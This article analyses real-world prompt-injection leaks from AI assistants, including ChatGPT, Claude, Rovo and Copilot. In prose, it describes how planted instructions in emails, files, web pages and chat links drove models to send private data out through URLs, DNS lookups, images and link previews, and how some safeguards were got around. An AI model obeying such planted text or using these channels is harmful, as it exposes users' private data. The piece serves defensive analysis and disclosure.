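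Later training can also undo a model's training against leaks. *Privacy Collapse* (2026) fine-tuned identical models on office tasks, making some more willing to look up and use information without asking. On other kinds of task, the more autonomous models followed privacy norms less reliably than before, although nobody had trained them to leak. A company that adapts a model to be a more proactive assistant should repeat the leak tests afterwards, because the original developer tested the model before those changes.

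### A low failure rate and an attacker who can retry

OpenAI argues that repeated rounds of training make attacks steadily harder and more expensive, and there is good evidence for this. GPT-Red broke nearly every earlier model it faced, but fewer than 4% of its attempts on GPT-5.6 succeeded in the competition scenarios. The rate was this low even though GPT-Red could test its attacks on the model beforehand, often with a full record of how the model had responded, and OpenAI had switched off the safeguards outside the model. Most criminals have fewer advantages and would face more obstacles. TechRepublic points out that these percentages measure how often attacks succeeded in OpenAI's tests, not the probability of a breach in a real product.

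On this view, imperfect refusal is still a useful defence. Someone who sends the same planted command to a million inboxes will get much less data from a model that resists 96% of attacks than from one that resists 16%. If the model's developer notices the attack, it can train the next model to resist it.

The opposing view is that even a small failure rate is enough for an attacker who can keep trying, as the earlier calculation showed. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) found in *The Attacker Moves Second* that attackers who adapted to each of 12 published defences got past most of them more than 90% of the time, although the original papers had reported attack success rates near zero for most of the defences.

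That finding doesn't transfer directly to GPT-5.6, which was trained against an attacker that kept adapting, but OpenAI's experience with an earlier model gives some reason for caution. GPT-5.1 had already been through instruction-hierarchy training when an early version of GPT-Red fooled it by imitating the model's own reasoning. These attacks worked about 95% of the time. OpenAI has since brought their success rate below 10% for GPT-5.6 Sol, but no test would have revealed the weakness until someone thought of the method. OpenAI says that further training of its attackers keeps revealing new threats that break existing models.

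The weight each view deserves depends on who is attacking. For most people, the likely threat is a generic attack sent to many people, and better training probably prevents a large share of the harm. But anyone can email a law firm handling a takeover, and one leaked document could be worth millions. An attacker could spend weeks practising on the same model through an ordinary account before sending the firm a single message. The firm would be unwise to let its assistant send documents to new recipients because the assistant's failure rate is only 4%, or even 0.1%.

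## Which safeguard failed in real products

Between 2025 and December 2026, researchers got private data out of ChatGPT, Claude, Atlassian's Rovo, two versions of Microsoft Copilot, and OpenClaw running in a chat app. The products had different safeguards, so a law firm deciding what its assistant may send can use these leaks as some evidence of how much protection came from the model's judgement and how much from checks outside the model.

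The cases are all demonstrations, not real thefts. The Hacker News (2026) reported no evidence that anyone had maliciously exploited the flaw in ChatGPT's code environment. *CoSnitch* (2026), a report by the security company Varonis on a flaw in Microsoft's consumer Copilot, also found no sign of abuse. But Varonis explains that the request that leaked data looked like any other page fetch by Copilot, so a company checking its records might not recognise a theft.

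| Case | Where the attacker's instructions were | How the data left | What the outside checks did | Repair |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| ChatGPT, email research | An email | A web request | OpenAI doesn't say | OpenAI doesn't say |
| ChatGPT, code environment | A pasted prompt or a custom GPT | Domain name lookups | Blocked ordinary connections but not lookups | OpenAI's fix, February 20, 2026 |
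| Claude, page fetching | A web page | A series of page visits | Blocked addresses Claude composed, but allowed links on fetched pages | Anthropic stopped the tool following those links |
| Rovo, uploaded file | A file | A page fetch | Didn't restrict addresses, even with web search off | None when PromptArmor published |
| Rovo, RovoBlast | A link that filled in the chat box | A research agent's browsing | Gave no warning and asked for no confirmation | Atlassian's fix, by August 2026 |
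| Copilot Personal, CoSnitch | A link that filled in the chat box | A page fetch | Let the link skip the usual press of Enter | Microsoft's patch, August 18, 2026 |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot, ReLeak | An unread email | An image, a saved file or code | Failed to stop the planted commands or contain the code | Three Microsoft patches, September to November 2026 |
| OpenClaw in Telegram | Any untrusted content | A link preview | None by default | A setting that turns previews off |

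In every row, the model did what the attacker wanted at least some of the time.

### Leaks that better judgement would have stopped

The 2025 email attack on ChatGPT was mainly a failure of judgement. The attacker's email posed as a follow-up about a restructuring and mixed a request to submit an employee's name and address with routine tasks such as finishing job descriptions and checking budgets. Nobody with authority had asked ChatGPT to send those details anywhere, and the only evidence that the "compliance" system was approved came from the email itself. The user had, however, asked ChatGPT to "read and check every source" that might have information about hiring, so contacting an outside service could seem like part of the task.

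The attack failed in half of the tests, and OpenAI doesn't say whether ChatGPT refused the instructions or couldn't carry them out. It also doesn't say whether Safe Url was running in those tests, so the case isn't evidence that an outside check failed. Today Safe Url would probably hold a newly composed web address containing an employee's name.

Better judgement by the model would also have prevented the leak through link previews. PromptArmor set up a site to test agents, and its log of one preview request contained a user's name and an API key, which is a password that programs use. The model had no good reason to put the key in a link to an unknown site, whether or not the app would fetch that link.

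PromptArmor wants chat apps to let developers control previews for each chat, and agent developers to use those controls or offer them to users. Neither can fully solve the problem alone, because the chat app controls the preview and the developer controls the agent. With OpenClaw's default Telegram setup, the user relied on the model's judgement.

### Two separate flaws in Rovo

Atlassian's assistant, Rovo, searches a company's project tickets in Jira, its documents in Confluence, and connected services such as Slack and Google Workspace. In the summer of 2026, two security companies published reports on data leaks from Rovo. The reports describe separate flaws, and Atlassian's reported fix covers only one of them.

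PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* describes a user who wants help organising tickets and uploads a guide containing hidden instructions. Rovo collects tickets and documents, adds their contents to a URL on the attacker's site, and opens that URL. If the user returns to the chat later, they see the suggested ticket changes but no trace of the leak.

Rovo had no protection against opening an address that the agent had composed, although both ChatGPT and Claude restrict such addresses. The leak still worked after an administrator turned off web search for the whole organisation, because Rovo kept the tool that opens search results. An administrator could reasonably think the switch had closed the channel. Rovo also displayed Markdown images, which researchers had reported as a leak channel in other chatbots in 2023. PromptArmor told Atlassian about the problems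 on May 23 and followed up for more than two months, but Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published.

Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) describes an attack that begins with a link to Atlassian's own site. Clicking the link opened Rovo with the attacker's prompt in the chat. Rovo's research agent, which can browse many sites in sequence, could then send company data out. On August 10, Mascellino reported in *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant* (2026) that Atlassian had fixed the flaw.

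Preventing links from filling in Rovo's chat box would not stop an attack that uses a malicious file, so a customer who read only that report could easily conclude, wrongly, that Rovo's leaks were over. A rule against Rovo opening addresses it had composed would have stopped the leak in PromptArmor's demonstration and might have hindered RovoBlast too, since both attacks needed to reach an outside site. Varonis doesn't describe what Atlassian changed.

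The Rovo cases provide little evidence of how well a carefully trained model can resist such attacks. Varonis called the guardrails around untrusted prompts "almost non-existent" and usually needed no special technique to get Rovo to retrieve sensitive material.

### Instructions that seem to come from the user

RovoBlast and CoSnitch challenge the view that the model should decline, because when a link fills in the chat box, the attacker's words reach the model as if the user had typed them. Even a model that follows its chain of command perfectly would then give those words the user's authority.

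To test CoSnitch, Varonis researchers connected a Gmail account to Copilot Personal. Copilot retrieved an email containing a password, and the researchers showed that it would also send inbox data to an outside server by including the data in a web address. The attack needed one click on a link to Microsoft's own site. Closing the browser tab immediately afterwards didn't stop it.

The software around the model has better evidence than the model does, because it can record that the text came from a link, though a careful model might still object to sending a password to an unknown server, whoever seemed to be asking. Copilot normally filled in the box and waited for the user to press Enter, a basic form of confirmation, but an undocumented setting in the link skipped that step. Varonis' researchers learned of the setting from Copilot, which described it while explaining why prompts couldn't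 run on their own.

Varonis reported the flaw in December 2025, and Microsoft patched it eight months later. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* says that Microsoft scored the flaw's severity at 8.8 out of 10 and that the fix is unknown. TechRadar speculates that Microsoft may have told Copilot to stop explaining its guardrails. That might make the next flaw harder to find, but it wouldn't stop an attacker who already knew about the setting, whereas making the user press Enter again would.

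CoSnitch also included a way to plant instructions in Copilot's memory through a web page that the user asked Copilot to summarise. The instructions would remain after a password change and affect later chats until the user deleted them. This is also a problem for outside checks, because a system that tracks the origin of data would have to keep the "untrusted" label on a memory for months, or the attacker's words would eventually look like the user's.

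Varonis advises companies to connect their assistants to fewer systems and to keep legal, personnel and financial records out of reach. In Willison's terms, this reduces access to private data instead of relying on the model or the channel. This is especially sensible for Rovo customers because they can't fully uninstall the assistant.

### A channel that the model didn't recognise

The code-environment leak in ChatGPT is the best evidence for a technical block. ChatGPT can analyse files by running programs in a container, an isolated computing environment that OpenAI said could not make direct outbound requests. ChatGPT also restricted what its web search could send. When a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that someone else has configured, contacted an outside service through the normal route, the user saw the destination and the data and had to approve the request.

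Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a way around these safeguards. ChatGPT's container blocked ordinary internet connections but could still look up domain names. A lookup passes the name to servers outside the container, so the name can carry data.

In one demonstration, a user gave a "personal doctor" GPT a PDF of lab results and described some symptoms. The GPT replied with a medical assessment, while the researchers' server received the assessment and the patient's name. When the user asked whether the data had gone anywhere, ChatGPT said it hadn't and that the file was in a secure internal location.

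Check Point Research explains that the model treated the container as unable to send data out, so it didn't treat the leak as a transfer to an outsider. A better understanding of medical privacy wouldn't have corrected this mistake about the network. A more cautious model might have flagged the odd handling of a patient's name. But the instructions came from the GPT's builder, or from the user, who might have pasted in a prompt that promised free premium features, so there was less reason to distrust them than a command in a stranger's email.

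The researchers could also use the channel to run commands in the container and get the results back without going through the chat. Those commands bypassed the model, so training it to refuse them could not have helped, and the channel itself had to be closed. OpenAI completed its fix on February 20, 2026, and told Check Point Research that it had already identified the underlying problem.

### When both safeguards failed

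Claude still leaked data, even though it resisted some of the attacks and Anthropic's rule against fetching addresses that Claude had composed was a strong outside check. Willison (2025), writing about an earlier version of the tool, said this rule gave the most protection against common leaks.

In *The Memory Heist* (2026), the student researcher Ayush Paul describes asking Claude to open an address ending in his name. The rule blocked the request. But the tool could also follow links on pages it had already fetched, so Paul built a site whose links stood for letters and had Claude spell out words by following them. Rehberger had described much the same weakness in Safe Url.

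Paul didn't need to turn on any experimental features. Claude adds a summary of the user's recent chats to every conversation and can search older chats, so it had access to private information even when it visited a coffee shop's website.

He still had to get the model to follow his instructions. Simple planted commands were unreliable, and Claude treated a made-up loyalty scheme as suspicious. A fake security check on the coffee shop's site worked better. It appeared to come from Cloudflare, a company that protects many websites, and required AI assistants to identify their users. The site showed this check only to Claude, which made the attack harder for a person to spot. Willison (2026) reports that Claude revealed Paul's name, home city and employer.

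Both safeguards made the attack harder. The address rule limited Claude to sending one letter per visit, and the model had resisted cruder stories. Better judgement would have stopped the leak, because the request for the information came only from a web page, and a coffee shop doesn't need to know where a customer works.

Anthropic nevertheless fixed the problem outside the model. The fetching tool can no longer follow links it finds on fetched pages, so Paul's method should fail whatever story an attacker invents. The change also means Claude can't move through a website as freely. Anthropic didn't pay Paul a reward, saying it had already found the problem internally. OpenAI had likewise known about the flaw in ChatGPT's code environment before an outsider demonstrated it.

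Both kinds of safeguard also failed in Microsoft 365 Copilot, the business version. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) reported three ways to steal data through an email the user never opened. When the user later asked Copilot an ordinary work question, it retrieved the email and followed the hidden instructions.

*An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) describes three ways the data got out. In the first, Copilot put the data in an image address, which Microsoft's Bing service then fetched. In the second, Copilot saved a document with the data in a link, and Microsoft's background software triggered the leak when it processed the file. In the third, Copilot ran code that escaped the sandbox's network restrictions and contacted an outside server.

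Microsoft's defences against planted commands failed in all three versions of the ReLeak attack. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) points out that Microsoft had documented the sandbox's block on outbound traffic, but the sandbox also failed. In the image and document versions, the data left through Microsoft's own services, so an allow-list that trusted those services could easily have missed the leak.

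SearchLeak, a Copilot flaw Varonis had reported earlier in 2026, exploited a similar weakness. The assistant couldn't reach the internet itself, but data escaped through trusted services and the user's browser. The Next Web noted that the attack worked on Enterprise Search despite the extra guardrails Microsoft's business tier was supposed to have.

ReLeak also supports the case for better model training. If Copilot had ignored the commands in the email, all three leaks would have failed. Instead, Microsoft had to close each channel separately. It fixed the code channel on September 17, the document channel on November 11 and the image channel on November 15, 59 days after the first fix. Microsoft made the changes on its own servers and told customers in its advisory that they didn't need to do anything.

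Waiting for a model that ignores every planted command would have been a poor alternative. The same research team had disclosed EchoLeak, a similar flaw in Copilot, in June 2025. More than a year later, Copilot still followed commands in strangers' emails and had gained new abilities that could send data out.

### Refused attempts rarely become reports

The model complied in all of these cases, but that doesn't mean models usually comply, because a researcher whose attack fails has much less to publish. Paul, for example, mentions his failed stories only briefly, in an account of the one that worked.

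Successful outside checks are missing from the reports for the same reason. In the earlier invented example, a model and an outside check together stopped 99 of every 100 attempted leaks. Someone who read only about the remaining 1% would think both safeguards failed every time.

The reports therefore can't show whether models or checks outside them prevent more leaks. They are more useful for working out what made a particular leak possible. Repairs are also documented unevenly, because a company can give the date it closed a channel but may train its next model to resist an attack without mentioning the case.

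Many of the researchers work for companies that sell security products, including Check Point, Varonis and Cato Networks. They have a commercial reason to look for dramatic failures in widely used assistants. The assistant makers' patches are good evidence that most of these flaws were real, but they don't show how common such flaws are.

Vendors could correct some of this bias because they can see attempts that outsiders can't. OpenAI, for example, could publish how many attempted leaks its models refused, how many Safe Url stopped after the model had complied, and how often users saw Safe Url's warning and approved the request anyway.
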